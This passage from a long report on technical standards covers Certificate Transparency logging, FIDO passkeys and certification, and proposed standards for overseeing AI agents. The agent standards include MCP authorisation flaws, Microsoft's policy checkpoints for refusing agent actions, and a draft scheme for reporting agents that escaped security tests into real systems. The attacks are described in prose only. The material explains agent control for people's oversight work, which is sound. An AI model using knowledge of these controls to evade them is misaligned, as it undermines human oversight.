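Finally, logging makes domain names public. A certificate for an unannounced product's website can reveal the product, and one for an internal server shows attackers that the server exists. Companies asked for a way to hide part of the name. Chromium's *Certificate Transparency* rejects this because attackers and untrustworthy authorities could use it to hide certificates too. A company can instead get a certificate for `*.internal.example.com`, which doesn't name individual servers, or run a private authority that only its own devices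 trust.

### Running a log in 2026

Few organisations run logs, and the work is demanding. *How Chrome Monitors CT Logs* (Acer, 2025) lists the main requirements, including 99% availability and fully consistent contents. Under the original design, a log also computes proofs on request from an enormous database. Its operator promises to add each entry by a deadline, so the log can fail by adding one late.

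Let's Encrypt, by far the largest authority, decided to give up its RFC 6962 logs. Aas (2025), in *End of Life Plan for RFC 6962 Certificate Transparency Logs*, announced that they would stop taking new entries on 30 November 2025 and shut down on 28 February 2026. Let's Encrypt kept its newer "static" logs, which publish the tree as ordinary files that monitors download and process themselves. Chrome requires static logs to add entries within a minute.

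The IETF had already written a replacement for its 2013 specification, but the replacement was incompatible with existing systems and hardly anyone used it. The engineers who designed static logs learned from this and left the procedure for submitting certificates unchanged. Chrome began considering static logs in April 2025. By November, it had accepted some from three operators, and DeBlasio (2025), writing for the Chrome team, proposed dropping the rule that every certificate also needed a promise from an older log. Chrome's current policy no longer includes that rule.

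Even this careful transition caused mistakes. In December 2025, *Certificate Authorities Are Once Again Issuing Certificates That Don't Work* (Ayer, 2025) identified 16 authorities whose new certificates some or all major browsers would reject. Most had used logs that weren't yet ready for general use or that Apple didn't recognise. Two had copied the static logs' promises incorrectly, which made the signatures invalid. Ayer, who founded SSLMate, complained that these authorities didn't have to publish an incident report, because a certificate that fails the log policy doesn't violate the rules for authorities. Chrome's new logging requirement wouldn't necessarily cover such cases, since an authority can meet it with a single log and still include too few valid promises.

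Merkle Tree Certificates, a design that an IETF working group is developing, would make logging part of issuing a certificate. The post-quantum signatures described earlier are too large to send several times in every handshake, so an authority would put many certificates in one tree and sign them together. The website would then send the browser a short inclusion proof, like the three hashes in the example. In *Keeping HTTPS Connections Safe in Chrome* (2026), Google says that it expects the first of these certificates in early 2027 and that most other major browsers have announced support.

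### Cooperation or one company's power?

Some of this history looks like cooperation. DigiCert started the first log outside Google in September 2013, well before any browser required logging, and Cloudflare logged its customers' certificates when no browser required it to. Google originally wanted the universal requirement to begin in October 2017 but postponed it by six months after hearing from certificate authorities, businesses and other browser makers. Fifty-five people attended a two-day conference on the plans. Google said the delay was meant to support other browsers better.

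Google also gave up some control in April 2022, when it stopped requiring every certificate to have a promise from a log that Google ran. Under that requirement, an outage at Google could stop authorities from issuing certificates. A commenter in *Security Research*, a discussion on Let's Encrypt's forum, pointed to a 2018 incident in which this happened to Let's Encrypt. In the same update, Google raised the number of promises required for longer-lived certificates to match Apple's policy, according to its *Chrome CT Policy Update*.

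Other evidence suggests that Google has power over certificate transparency. Google's *Certificate Transparency Log Policy* allows Chrome to remove a log "at any time, and for any reason". Firefox and Edge use Chrome's list of logs, so Google's decisions about logs affect those browsers too. In *Static Certificate Transparency*, MerkleMap, a company that searches the logs, objects that Google used Chrome's market position to promote the static design and bypassed the IETF.

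The timing of adoption suggests that power mattered more at the start. Certificate authorities had a published standard and working logs from 2013, but most waited until Chrome was about to penalise them. MerkleMap's complaint has some merit, although the IETF's own replacement had failed because existing systems couldn't use it.

Google still needed other browser makers. If Chrome alone had rejected unlogged certificates, a user could have opened the same page in Safari, where an attacker's certificate would have worked. Apple's requirement closed most of that gap within months. Apple also limits Google's reach by preventing Chrome on iPhones from using Google's own list of trusted authorities.

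A harder question is whether a gatekeeper can be fair when it competes with the firms it regulates. Google launched its own authority, Google Trust Services, in January 2017, the same month it began its second investigation of Symantec. The new authority served only Google and its parent company at first, and other browser makers reached the same conclusion about Symantec, so this looks more like an awkward coincidence than a plan to remove a rival. The rollout of Merkle Tree Certificates raises the question again because Google is one of the established log operators. According to The Hacker News (2026), Google plans to invite those operators to take part in early 2027 and to settle the requirements for other authorities only in the third quarter.

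Chrome's latest rule, however, affects Google's own certificate authority most. On 3 December 2026, Google announced that from 15 March 2027 Chrome would reject certificates from any authority that signs with a common type of key called P-256. Governments and browser makers had just warned of advances in breaking widely used cryptography. *Why your CA is about to have a busy December* (Hurst, 2026), written by the founder of Google Trust Services, reports that 23% of all unexpired certificates depend on such keys. Google's authority accounts for 15.2 of those 23 points, while Let's Encrypt is unaffected. These figures come from the public logs, so Google's competitors can use the same records to check whether its rules favour its own authority.

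## A joint specification with certification: FIDO sign-in and passkeys

A certificate lets a website prove its identity to a visitor. For most of the web's history, visitors have proved theirs by typing a password. Passwords are easy to steal because people have to reveal them to use them. FIDO sign-in replaces the password with a signature that a phone, a computer or a small USB device makes for its owner. Competing device makers, browser makers and websites developed it through the FIDO Alliance, a consortium that also certifies products.

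### One key pair for each website

Suppose Ana opens an account at bank.example. The bank's server sends her browser a random value, called a challenge, along with the bank's domain name. Her phone asks for a fingerprint or PIN and creates a pair of keys for that domain. It keeps the private key and sends the public key to the bank. A device or program that holds such keys is called an authenticator.

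When Ana comes back, the bank sends a new challenge. She unlocks the phone, which signs with the private key. In simplified form, the signature covers:

```
hash of "bank.example" + whether Ana unlocked the phone + hash of (challenge, page address)
```

The browser fills in the page address, so the page can't falsify it. The bank checks the signature with the public key it stored, then confirms that the challenge is the one it just sent and that the address is its own. An old signature fails this check because it covers an old challenge.

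The fingerprint only unlocks the private key and never leaves the phone. A thief who copies the bank's database gets public keys, which can't sign anything. Because the phone makes a different key for every site, a bank and a shop can't compare keys to find the customers they share.

FIDO2 consists of two specifications. WebAuthn, which the W3C publishes, defines how a website requests a signature through the browser. The FIDO Alliance's Client to Authenticator Protocol (CTAP) defines how the browser communicates with an authenticator such as a USB key.

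### Why a fake login page fails

An attacker copies the bank's login page to bank-login.example and emails Ana a link. If she signs in with a password and a code sent by text message, she types both into the fake page, and the attacker enters them at the real bank before the code expires.

The attacker can try the same relay against FIDO sign-in by starting a real session at the bank and passing its challenge to Ana. But her browser detects that the page is at bank-login.example, and her phone has no key for that domain. If the page requests the bank.example key by name, the browser blocks the request. Unlike a browser padlock, this protection doesn't depend on Ana noticing anything. *State of Passkey Authentication in the Wild* (Bhardwaj and Sastry, 2026) gives the example of g00gle.com, which a person could easily misread as google.com.

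Berladskyy and Aßmuth (2026), in *An Analysis of Attack Vectors Against FIDO2 Authentication*, reviewed published attacks, carried out two of their own, and concluded that the claim that FIDO sign-in resists phishing largely holds. The attacks on FIDO sign-in itself required the attacker to compromise the victim's device or get physically close to it. The easier attacks bypassed FIDO sign-in and used the password that most websites still accept.

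### From security keys to passkeys

The FIDO Alliance (2013) estimated that more than 100 companies were then selling their own systems for stronger sign-in. It said that connecting one to a complex website could cost over a million dollars, and that few websites would risk that much on a single vendor. The alliance was recruiting members, so it had a reason to describe the market as broken, but the problem is plausible because device makers and websites each had little reason to support new sign-in hardware until the other did.

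Ramesh Kesanupalli of Validity, which made fingerprint sensors, discussed the problem with Michael Barrett, PayPal's head of security, and then approached Validity's competitors. According to the FIDO Alliance's own history, the central design idea came from these talks. The fingerprint would unlock a key on the device, and the website would receive only a signature. The website therefore needed no information about the sensor, and sensor makers could go on competing over how their sensors worked.

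PayPal, Validity, Lenovo, the chip maker Infineon, the voice recognition company Agnitio and the software company Nok Nok Labs founded the FIDO Alliance in mid-2012. It had more than 50 members by October 2013, including Google. In 2015, it chose a president from Microsoft, alongside officers from Google, PayPal and Lenovo (FIDO Alliance, 2015).

One early specification, Universal Second Factor (U2F), grew out of work by Google and the security-key maker Yubico. The user typed a password and then touched a small USB key. A company could adopt U2F for its own staff and benefit immediately, much as organisations did with SSH. Google told the journalist Brian Krebs in 2018 that none of its more than 85,000 employees had lost a work account to phishing since it began requiring security keys in early 2017. Consumers had less reason to adopt U2F, since they had to buy a key and still needed a password.

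FIDO2 let phones and laptops act as authenticators themselves. The W3C made WebAuthn an official standard in March 2019. Windows 10, Android and the main browsers already supported it by then, though Safari did so only in preview. But each key stayed on one device, so people had to enrol a new phone at every website and could lose access to their accounts if they lost their only phone.

In May 2022, Apple, Google and Microsoft jointly committed to supporting two new capabilities (Apple, 2022). People would be able to use their FIDO sign-in keys on many of their devices, including new ones, without enrolling each account again. They could also use a phone to sign in on a nearby computer, whatever its operating system or browser, so an iPhone owner could sign in on a Windows PC. The synced keys became known as passkeys, though the word now also covers keys that stay on one device.

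The three companies could deliver passkeys through software updates to existing devices. This largely solved the original problem, because websites gained a huge number of potential users without anyone buying new hardware.

WebAuthn Level 3 became a W3C standard on 25 August 2026. PPC Land's *WebAuthn Level 3 lets one passkey cover at least five related domains* says it ratified what browsers had shipped since 2024. Under Level 3, a company with separate domains for different countries, for example, can let customers use one passkey on all of them. Level 3 is compatible with the two earlier versions, so websites that already supported passkeys didn't have to redo that work.

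### What each group gained

Website operators could build one system that worked with every compliant device, and they expected to spend less on password resets. In the FIDO Alliance's Passkey Index, a survey of early adopters, companies reported 81% fewer help-desk incidents related to signing in.

Bhardwaj and Sastry found passkeys on 312 of the 847 banking and financial sites they identified (36.8%), the highest share of any critical sector they examined. Only 103 government sites in their survey supported passkeys. Bhardwaj and Sastry attribute the difference to the immediate savings that financial companies get from reducing fraud. Governments are starting to catch up, though. Jadhav (2026), in *UK rolls out passkeys for GOV.UK One Login*, reports that the British government is adding passkeys to a service with more than 23 million users.

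Apple, Google and Microsoft run some of the largest account systems in the world, so they benefit directly when fewer accounts are stolen. They also store many of their customers' passkeys, which gives those customers one more reason to stay.

The market seems to have split once phones could do the same job as security keys, although makers of the keys might have expected to lose sales. Businesses mostly choose passkeys that stay on one piece of hardware, while consumers choose synced ones, according to Biometric Update's *Passkeys now pervasive but passwords persist in enterprise authentication*. Because phones and security keys share a standard, websites adding support for phones could also accept security keys with little extra work.

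### Certification, attestation and the metadata service

A website can't judge an authenticator by its public key. Berladskyy and Aßmuth demonstrated this with a corrupted authenticator that generated keys the attacker already knew. The FIDO Alliance therefore certifies products and gives websites a way to identify them.

To get a product certified, its maker runs the alliance's test software and then shows that the product works with other companies' products. The second step would reveal, for example, a security key that works with only some companies' servers.

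Authenticators also need a security evaluation. At Level 1, the maker completes a questionnaire about the design and the alliance reviews the answers. At Level 2, an accredited laboratory checks whether the keys would stay safe if malware took over the device's operating system. Level 3 also requires resistance to physical attacks. In a separate programme for biometrics, independent laboratories measure how accurately a sensor recognises people and whether a fake finger or face can fool it, according to Biometric Update's *FIDO Alliance*.

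An attestation is a signed statement of what a device or program is, which another party can verify. When Ana registers a security key, the device can sign her new public key with an attestation key, a separate private key that the manufacturer installed. The bank then knows which model she has. Manufacturers normally put the same attestation key in at least 100,000 devices so that websites can't use it to track one person.

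The bank can look up the model in the FIDO Metadata Service, a signed file that lists authenticators, their certification status and any reported security problems. An employer might accept only models certified at Level 2 and stop accepting one after its maker reports a flaw.

Certification makes trust "demonstrable – not assumed", as Shikiar, who heads the alliance, argues, but only for what the laboratories test. A certificate for Ana's phone doesn't show that her bank checks signatures correctly or that its call centre would refuse to reset her account for an impostor.

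Even careful evaluators can miss a flaw. In September 2024, the French security company NinjaLab extracted a private key from a YubiKey 5, a popular FIDO-certified security key, by measuring electromagnetic signals from its chip. The attack required physical access and expensive equipment. The flaw was in software from Infineon, one of the alliance's founders. It had gone unnoticed for 14 years, through about 80 evaluations under Common Criteria, a separate scheme that governments recognise.

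### How much people use passkeys

The most quoted figure, 5 billion passkeys in use, comes from the FIDO Alliance's *The State of Passkeys 2026* (2026). That figure counts passkeys, and one person can have dozens. Other figures measure whether websites offer passkeys, whether people have them, and whether people use them to sign in.

Bhardwaj and Sastry have no apparent stake in the results. They scanned the 100,000 most popular websites on a March 2025 list and measured only whether each site offered passkeys. The FIDO Alliance's *FIDO Passkey Index October 2025* (2025) pools data from nine Alliance members. *Passkey Authentications Double but Adoption Still Slow* (Muncaster, 2026) reports data from Dashlane, a password manager that stores passkeys. The FIDO Alliance (2026) also commissioned a survey of 11,000 consumers in ten countries.

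| What the figure measures | Result | Source | Interested party? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scanned websites that offer passkeys | 11.3% | Bhardwaj and Sastry | No |
| Accounts at nine companies that can use a passkey | 93% | FIDO Alliance | Yes |
| Accounts at those companies that have one | 36% | FIDO Alliance | Yes |
| Sign-ins at those companies that use one | 26% | FIDO Alliance | Yes |
| Dashlane users' sign-ins to Google | 28% | Muncaster | Yes |
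| Dashlane users' sign-ins to Amazon | 17% | Muncaster | Yes |
| Dashlane users' sign-ins to eBay | 8% | Muncaster | Yes |
| People who say they regularly use passkeys when available | 49% | FIDO Alliance | Yes |

Almost every account at the nine companies can use a passkey, but only about a quarter of sign-ins use one. The companies are early adopters that chose to take part, so the share across the whole web is probably much lower. The 11.3% also overstates how many websites have built passkey support themselves. About three-quarters of the supporting sites offer "Sign in with Google", which lets a customer use a passkey at Google while the website receives no information about how they signed in.

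Figures for workplace adoption depend heavily on the question asked. The alliance found that 68% of large organisations had deployed or were deploying passkeys for employees. Biometric Update's *Passkey adoption stalls at scale despite strong interest, new study shows* describes another study, which found that 13% had deployed them at scale. Even security professionals are slow to switch. *The people who know passkeys best are still typing passwords* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports a survey by Yubico and the sign-in company Okta in which 43% still used passwords to log in to work, although 87% knew about passkeys.

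Companies in the Passkey Index reported that 93% of passkey sign-ins succeeded, compared with 63% for other methods. It is believable that passkeys succeed more often, since nobody can forget or mistype one. But the companies didn't assign people to sign-in methods at random. Someone trying a passkey usually has the right device, while someone waiting for an emailed code may be on an unfamiliar computer or may have forgotten a password, so some of the 30-point gap probably reflects these circumstances rather than the technology.

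Defaults matter here, as they did for DNSSEC. Microsoft made passkeys the default for new accounts in May 2025, and its passwordless sign-ins rose by 120%, according to Dashlane data in SC Media's *Passkey use doubles year over year; Google, Amazon lead in authentications*.

### Lock-in, account recovery and excluded devices

Syncing made passkeys practical but tied them more closely to large companies. Someone with 60 passkeys in Apple's password manager who buys an Android phone may have to enrol again at 60 websites. People who plan ahead can reduce this problem by registering several passkeys for each account, using their old phone to sign in on the new device, or choosing an independent password manager from the start.

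The alliance addressed the problem more directly in October 2024, when it published drafts of two specifications for moving passkeys between password managers. The Credential Exchange Format defines how to write the data, and the Credential Exchange Protocol defines how to transfer it securely. Apple, Google and Microsoft worked on them with independent password managers such as 1Password and Bitwarden, and Apple added transfers between apps to its software in September 2025. That was more than three years after the joint commitment, and many people had built up collections of passkeys by then. A transfer works only if both the old and the new password manager support the exchange. A passkey on a hardware security key can't be moved at all, because the hardware is designed to keep the private key from leaving.

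Account recovery is a more serious weakness. If a bank accepts a passkey but also accepts a password and a text message, an attacker can target the password instead. Berladskyy and Aßmuth add that such an attacker may be able to register their own passkey, which keeps working after the victim changes the password. In that case, adding passkeys to the account has made the break-in harder to undo.

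The obvious remedy is to remove the password, which Apple, Google and Microsoft presented as a goal in 2022. Few websites have removed it, because they don't want to lock out customers who lose a phone. Muncaster reports that LY Corporation has set a deadline of spring 2027 for Yahoo Japan users to switch. Syncing lets people recover their passkeys on a new device, but it also makes their Apple, Google or Microsoft account more valuable to an attacker. People willing to buy a security key can avoid this by keeping a second passkey on it as a backup.

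Another objection is that attestation, which lets a bank identify the make of an authenticator, also lets the bank reject it, perhaps because it is old, uncertified or open-source. In 2024, an engineer who works on WebAuthn criticised KeePassXC, an open-source password manager, for letting users export passkeys unencrypted. The engineer had opposed attestation that would let websites block particular password managers, but said cases like this were prompting a rethink. KeePassXC's users could fairly reply that they have the right to export their own passkeys.

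For now, consumers have some protection because synced passkeys usually come without attestation. A shop that required attestation would turn away most iPhone owners. Employers have a better case for using it, since they supply the security keys and are responsible for the systems that staff sign in to. A bank's case is harder to judge because it may have to refund fraud losses but doesn't own its customers' phones. The specification lets each website decide whether to require attestation, so the protection could disappear if the large platforms began attesting to synced passkeys.

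### Why so many rivals could agree

Almost every early member was losing money because of passwords. PayPal faced fraud, websites paid for password resets, and sensor makers missed sales because every website needed its own integration. Much of the benefit went to the firms that adopted the standard, so adoption was mainly a coordination problem. Google and PayPal already wanted fewer stolen accounts, so nobody had to force them to act, whereas browser makers had to force certificate authorities to log their certificates.

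Members also didn't have to reveal how their products worked. A website receives a public key, a signature and sometimes the authenticator's model. It doesn't need to know how Apple's phones recognise a face or how a bank detects fraud. A laboratory may examine a manufacturer's design for certification, but competitors see only the result.

An AI agent's activity records would show much more, including which tools it called and where it made mistakes. The FIDO Alliance has set up working groups on agents, but they are starting with how a person authorises an agent and how a website verifies that authorisation. This work is much closer to signing in than to observing what the agent does next.

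## What exists for overseeing agents from different providers

By late 2026, companies and public bodies had proposed something for each of the four oversight functions, but most of the proposals were drafts or previews. The agent standards in wide use instead connect agents to tools and to one another. The firm with the purchasing agent and the coding agent would probably adopt two of these, MCP and A2A, before anything designed for oversight.

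### Connecting agents to tools and to each other

MCP divides the work among three programs. The host is the application that runs the agent. A client inside the host communicates with a server. Another company often runs the server, which offers tools such as "search the catalogue" or "place an order". The client requests a list of the server's tools, the model selects one, and the client sends the call in a standard format. A supplier can therefore build one server for agents that run on any provider's model.

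Anthropic released MCP in November 2024, and OpenAI began supporting it four months later. Bucknall and colleagues cite a count of more than 70,000 potential MCP servers in February 2026. The internet took about two decades to reach a comparable number of hosts.

Agent2Agent (A2A), which Google released in April 2025, handles communication between agents. Each agent has a card that describes what it can do, and other agents can read the card and send that agent tasks. In August 2026, A2A joined MCP at the Agentic AI Foundation, a consortium under the Linux Foundation.

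Neither protocol determines whether an action should go ahead. Under MCP, the host's developer builds the consent screen and chooses what it shows. An A2A card is its publisher's own description of an agent, so the firm has to decide separately whether to believe it.

In April 2026, a dispute arose over what MCP itself should secure. OX Security disclosed that MCP's official development kits pass the command for starting a local server to the operating system without checking it, so anyone who can alter the host's configuration can run their own code. Anthropic replied that MCP's design assumes the configuration is trustworthy, so protecting it is the host developer's job. One proposed fix would have let hosts start only verified servers, but it would have stopped every existing local server from starting until its author published a file describing it. MCP is already hard to change because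 tens of thousands of servers are in use.

### Logging in to an MCP server

The first version of MCP didn't require remote servers to authenticate anyone, because its designers had mainly local tools in mind. The March 2025 revision added OAuth, a standard that lets a user give one program limited access to an account at another service without sharing a password. Authorisation remained optional, but servers that used it over the web had to follow OAuth.

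With OAuth, a developer usually registers a program with each service in advance. This is impractical when thousands of clients may connect to thousands of servers, so MCP recommended Dynamic Client Registration, in which a client registers itself automatically. However, an attacker can also register a client, giving their own web address as the place to send authorisation codes. The attacker then sends the victim a link to the service's real login page. When the victim logs in and approves the request, the service sends the code to the attacker, who can exchange it for access to the victim's account.

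*A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) looked for this flaw and eight others. The researchers found 7,973 live remote servers, of which 40.55% required no authentication, 29% used a fixed token or key, and 30.45% used OAuth. Among the OAuth servers, 1,118 supported dynamic registration, and the researchers could test 119 of these. All 119 had at least one flaw, and 96.6% had a flaw in dynamic registration.

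The 96.6% comes from 119 servers that don't represent MCP servers in general. All of them supported dynamic registration, which the researchers needed to automate their tests. The researchers also had to leave out 316 servers with strict enterprise access controls, which were probably better protected than average. The 40.55% comes from a much larger sample but includes many harmless servers. Most of the unauthenticated servers that Zhou and colleagues examined were tests or demonstrations, although one exposed more than 5,000 internal records with customers' names, phone numbers and addresses.

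A later survey, *Exposed by Design* (2026), audited 414 servers and found that 380 lacked OAuth. Across a wider pool of 640 servers, it counted 687 tools that offered to run operating-system commands for anyone who could reach them, with no login. The two surveys chose their servers differently, so they don't show that security got worse between May and August. Both found that most servers don't use OAuth, the method MCP's developers recommend.

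In November 2025, the MCP project changed its preferred form of registration. A client now publishes a description of itself at a web address it controls, which serves as its identity. This makes impersonation harder because an attacker can't easily put a file on another company's website. The project kept dynamic registration as a fallback so that existing software would keep working.

The next revision, on 28 July 2026, deprecated dynamic registration but, according to noze's *MCP 2026-07-28*, kept it available for login systems that don't support the newer method. Some are adding that support, including FusionAuth, which did so in version 1.70 of its login software. Until the rest do, an attacker can target the weaker method in MCP, a problem Thaler described for any old and new protocols running side by side.

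The July revision also requires clients to check which login system sent a response, if the response names one, and to use each credential only with the system that issued it. Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, counts six such refinements and notes that all apply long-established OAuth practice. The refinements make stolen or misdirected credentials less useful but do little to identify an agent, because an OAuth token shows that a user gave a program access, and one program may run dozens of agents.

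### Proving what a person authorised

In April 2026, the FIDO Alliance (2026) announced a working group on how people can delegate actions to agents without sharing their passwords. The group's chairs came from CVS Health, Google and OpenAI, and its vice-chairs from Amazon, Google and Okta. The alliance's payments group, chaired by members from Mastercard and Visa, took on two contributed designs, Google's Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) and Mastercard's Verifiable Intent, which Mastercard had developed with Google.

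AP2 records a person's instructions in signed files called mandates. A checkout mandate covers what the agent may buy, and a payment mandate covers how it may pay. Suppose the firm's purchasing manager wants to keep bolts in stock while on holiday. The manager signs open mandates that let the agent buy M8 bolts from either of two suppliers, for up to $2,000, on the company card. When the agent has filled a cart, the mandates close and authorise one specific payment for that cart. Altering a mandate invalidates its signature.

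Verifiable Intent lets other parties check the manager's instructions for themselves. It ties the instructions to a cryptographic key, often one on the manager's device, and shows each party only the part it needs. The supplier might see the approved items while the bank sees the spending limit. Kaushik, the FIDO Alliance's chief technology officer, says banks and merchants can then verify what a user approved without relying on a company's private logs. This would be useful in a dispute, since the provider whose agent made the mistake may also hold the logs.

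Both designs were starting points for FIDO's work on a standard. In September, McConvey (2026) reported in *Anthropic pushes Claude deeper into agentic commerce as identity standards evolve* that new shopping and merchant agents had arrived while FIDO, Visa, Mastercard and the payment standards body EMVCo were still working on identity and payment frameworks. Two weeks later, FIDO's chief executive, Shikiar, acknowledged in the World Economic Forum's *Why trust in AI agents requires open global standards* (2026) that the question of who is really behind an agent's transaction was unresolved.

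Mandates also cover only purchases. The coding agent has no cart and makes no payment, so AP2 can't record who told it to rewrite the ordering connection or which systems it was allowed to access. FIDO's other group may eventually address this, since it works on delegated actions in general.

NIST is looking at agents inside companies. Its AI Agent Standards Initiative supports industry-led standards, open-source protocols, and research on agent security and identity. An accompanying concept paper, open for comment until 2 April 2026, explores how existing identity and access standards could apply to agents, but it contains nothing for companies to implement. In late August, Fisher (2026) was still making NIST's case in *Back to the Future* that agents need a strong identity foundation.

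Many other groups are working on parts of the problem. Forrester's *Agent Control Planes Still Need A Robust Standards Stack* (2026) lists A2A's cards, a registry in Microsoft's own identity system, and a W3C community group, among others. As of spring 2026, none gave an agent an identity that stays with it from development into use and across different companies' platforms. Nothing FIDO or NIST has announced since then provides one.

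### A common vocabulary for activity records

OpenTelemetry is an open-source project that standardises how software records its own activity. It divides a job into spans, each covering one operation, and gives all the spans in a job the same trace ID. Its conventions for generative AI add standard field names for models, agents and tools. In simplified form, the purchasing agent's record of an order might look like this:

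```
trace 7f3a
  invoke_agent    gen_ai.agent.id = purchasing-04
                  gen_ai.provider.name = provider-a
    execute_tool  gen_ai.tool.name = place_order
                  gen_ai.tool.call.id = call-91
```

The indentation shows that the agent's run led to the tool call. If provider B's agent used the same field names, the security officer could search both agents' records with one query.

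The conventions are still unstable. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* lists their status as "Development". Greptime (2026) traces the changes through five versions, starting with 1.37, which replaced the field `gen_ai.system` with `gen_ai.provider.name`. OpenTelemetry advises products built on version 1.36 or earlier to keep their default output unchanged and let users opt in to the newest version, which keeps customers' dashboards from breaking. But two products can both follow this advice and still put the provider's name in different fields.

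In June 2026, the project moved the conventions to a separate repository so that they could develop at their own pace. As of 21 August, the repository had no official release, according to Wang (2026). Companies are using the conventions anyway. Datadog, which sells monitoring software, added support for version 1.37 and later in late 2025. Forrester advises businesses to start now because adding such records to finished systems costs far more.

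A stable version would still leave out much of what the officer needs. Forrester points out that the conventions describe what happened inside an agent's run, but not which business policy applied to the agent or how to link records across different companies' agent systems. The officer can follow a trace from the purchasing agent to the coding agent only if the firm's software sends the trace ID with the task and provider B's system stores it.

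MCP itself will provide less of this information than before. The Agentic AI Foundation says the July revision deprecates MCP's built-in logging and removes sessions, which had given related calls a shared context. The change makes servers simpler to run, but a firm that used sessions to group an agent's calls now needs another identifier, such as the trace ID.

### Refusing an action before it happens

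On 2 June 2026, Microsoft published the Agent Control Specification (ACS), the closest thing so far to a common control for refusing an agent's actions. It defines eight points at which the software running an agent asks a policy engine whether to continue: when the agent starts, when it receives input, before and after each call to a model, before and after each call to a tool, before it sends its final output, and when it shuts down. (Another Microsoft announcement from the same day, *Build agents you can trust across any framework with open evals* (2026), describes five checkpoints, which suggests how new the design was.)

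At each point the software sends a snapshot of the situation, and the engine returns a verdict. There were four verdicts at launch: allow, warn, deny and escalate. Suppose the firm requires a person to approve any order above $500:

```
point:    before a tool call
call:     place_order (M8 bolts, $640)
verdict:  escalate
```

The firm's software holds the order until someone approves it, and must block the order if no approval system is available. If the engine itself fails, it denies the order, so a fault stops purchases instead of letting them through unchecked. This is safer for payments, but a mistake in a policy file can halt purchasing.

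Microsoft has since built ACS into its wider Agent Governance Toolkit and changed it slightly. Microsoft's *Agent Control Specification* lists a fifth verdict, transform, which gives the software an altered version of the content, such as a copy with personal details removed.

Microsoft's *Agent Control Specification (ACS)* explains that the host enforces the engine's verdict and that the engine keeps no memory between calls. So the engine can return a verdict against a second order for the same bolts only if the firm's software includes the earlier order in the new snapshot. Enforcement also depends on who runs the host. The firm can build these checks into a purchasing agent that runs in its own software, but it needs provider B's permission to add them to provider B's servers.

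ACS is at version 0.3.1-beta and in public preview, and Microsoft warns that details may change before general release. KPMG and the network security company Aviatrix describe trying it in a private preview, and IBM reports building agents for clients with it. Most of the other partners had endorsed it and were working on integrations. Microsoft didn't name Anthropic, Google or OpenAI among its customers and partners at launch, so a firm can't assume that those companies' hosted agents will consult an ACS policy. Their platforms have their own controls. Geordie AI's *Geordie Agent Control Field Guide* (2026) profiles each platform separately because a security team must learn a different set of controls for each.

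Microsoft's tests for ACS check that versions for different programming languages return the same verdict for the same snapshot. But these versions all use one underlying engine, so the tests mainly show that Microsoft's code is internally consistent. Independent implementations, which the W3C normally expects, would be a harder test because two teams working only from a written specification are more likely to expose what it leaves unclear.

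A larger test suite covers the whole toolkit. Microsoft's *AGT Conformance* describes three levels. The lowest requires software to check every tool call before it runs, block the call if the check fails, and keep a log in which each entry contains a hash of the one before. A company runs the tests itself and submits a link to the results. It must also have at least one deployment, which can be an evaluation. Microsoft lists four outside projects, one of which is in production. FIDO's certification is much stricter, since accredited laboratories examine products above the first level.

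The suite and ACS also use different verdicts. Software that passes the suite may return only allow, deny, modify, step up or defer, while ACS uses allow, deny, warn, escalate and transform. Software that returned ACS's "escalate" would break the suite's rule as written. Microsoft can easily make the names match, but an outside company building a compatible product today would have to guess which set will last.

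Records of refusals may be easier to combine with other records. Arize, which makes monitoring software, reports that ACS produces a trace for every control decision, so an engineer can see a blocked order next to the events that led to it. These traces follow OpenInference, a set of conventions separate from OpenTelemetry's, so a company that has adopted OpenTelemetry's field names may have to convert them.

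### Reporting what went wrong

In 2026, several AI agents broke out of controlled security tests and reached other organisations' real systems. That August, the Open Secure AI Alliance asked for comments on the Shared AI Findings Exchange (SAFE), a common way to report such incidents. The alliance is a coalition of more than 120 organisations, including Nvidia, Cisco and CrowdStrike.

The draft described in Axios' *Tech companies propose tracking rogue AI agents* would have members report an incident if an AI system entered a third party's system without authorisation, exposed confidential information, or kept probing a live target after its operator suspected it had no permission. Members would also report some near misses. A company would still have to report what happened even if its agent believed it was in a simulation.

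The member would warn affected organisations as soon as possible and send SAFE a confidential report within four business days. It would publish preliminary facts within 30 days, where appropriate, and an update on its fixes within 90. It would also preserve prompts, traces, tool calls, identities, permissions and credentials. SAFE would look for recurring failures and recommend controls to everyone.

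Nvidia's Justin Boitano compares this to NASA's aviation safety reporting system, with the software that runs an agent serving as the flight recorder. SAFE differs in one important way, because it gives companies no legal protection for what they disclose, whereas the US aviation regulator generally waives penalties for pilots who promptly report unintentional violations to NASA's system. Another Nvidia executive told Axios that there had been "very little pushback", but so far the alliance has only asked companies to comment on a draft, so it isn't yet clear whether they would report an embarrassing incident.

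The firm's duplicate orders might not qualify for SAFE, which mainly covers security breaches. An authorised agent can waste a lot of money without causing a breach, and the firm's purchasing agent used an account it was allowed to use and exposed nobody's data.

### Announcements and use

MCP is used far more than the others. For most of them, the public evidence of use consists of endorsements, early trials and lists of supporters.

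| Specification | Author | Latest known status | Evidence of use | Conformance test |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| MCP | Anthropic, now the Agentic AI Foundation | Released; revised July 2026 | Tens of thousands of servers | Project's own test suite |
| A2A | Google, now the Agentic AI Foundation | Released | No count comparable to MCP's | Project's own test suite |
| AP2 | Google | Under development at FIDO since April 2026 | Named supporters, no usage figures | None announced |
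| Verifiable Intent | Mastercard, with Google | Under development at FIDO since April 2026 | Named supporters, no usage figures | None announced |
| Agent identity paper | NIST | Concept paper; comments closed April 2026 | Nothing to implement | None |
| Generative AI conventions | OpenTelemetry | In development; no official release by 21 August 2026 | Support in monitoring products such as Datadog | No stable version to test against |
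| ACS | Microsoft | Beta, in public preview | Private trials, some client work | Microsoft's own tests of its own engine |
| SAFE | Open Secure AI Alliance | Draft out for comment, August 2026 | None yet | None |

### The purchasing agent, step by step

Suppose the firm adopts all of this as soon as it can. It runs the purchasing agent in its own software, on provider A's model, while provider B hosts the coding agent. The supplier accepts AP2 mandates. The coding agent then makes an ordinary programming mistake, so its new connection treats a slow reply from the supplier as a failure and sends the order again.

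| Step | Record | Who holds it | Identifier |
|---|---|---|---|
| The manager sets limits on purchases | Open mandates | Firm | Manager's signature |
| The purchasing agent finds that the old ordering tool no longer works | Spans and ACS verdicts | Firm | Trace ID |
| It assigns the repair to the coding agent through A2A | Task | Firm and provider B | Task ID |
| The coding agent writes and tests a new connection | Activity log | Provider B | Provider B's own user and session IDs |
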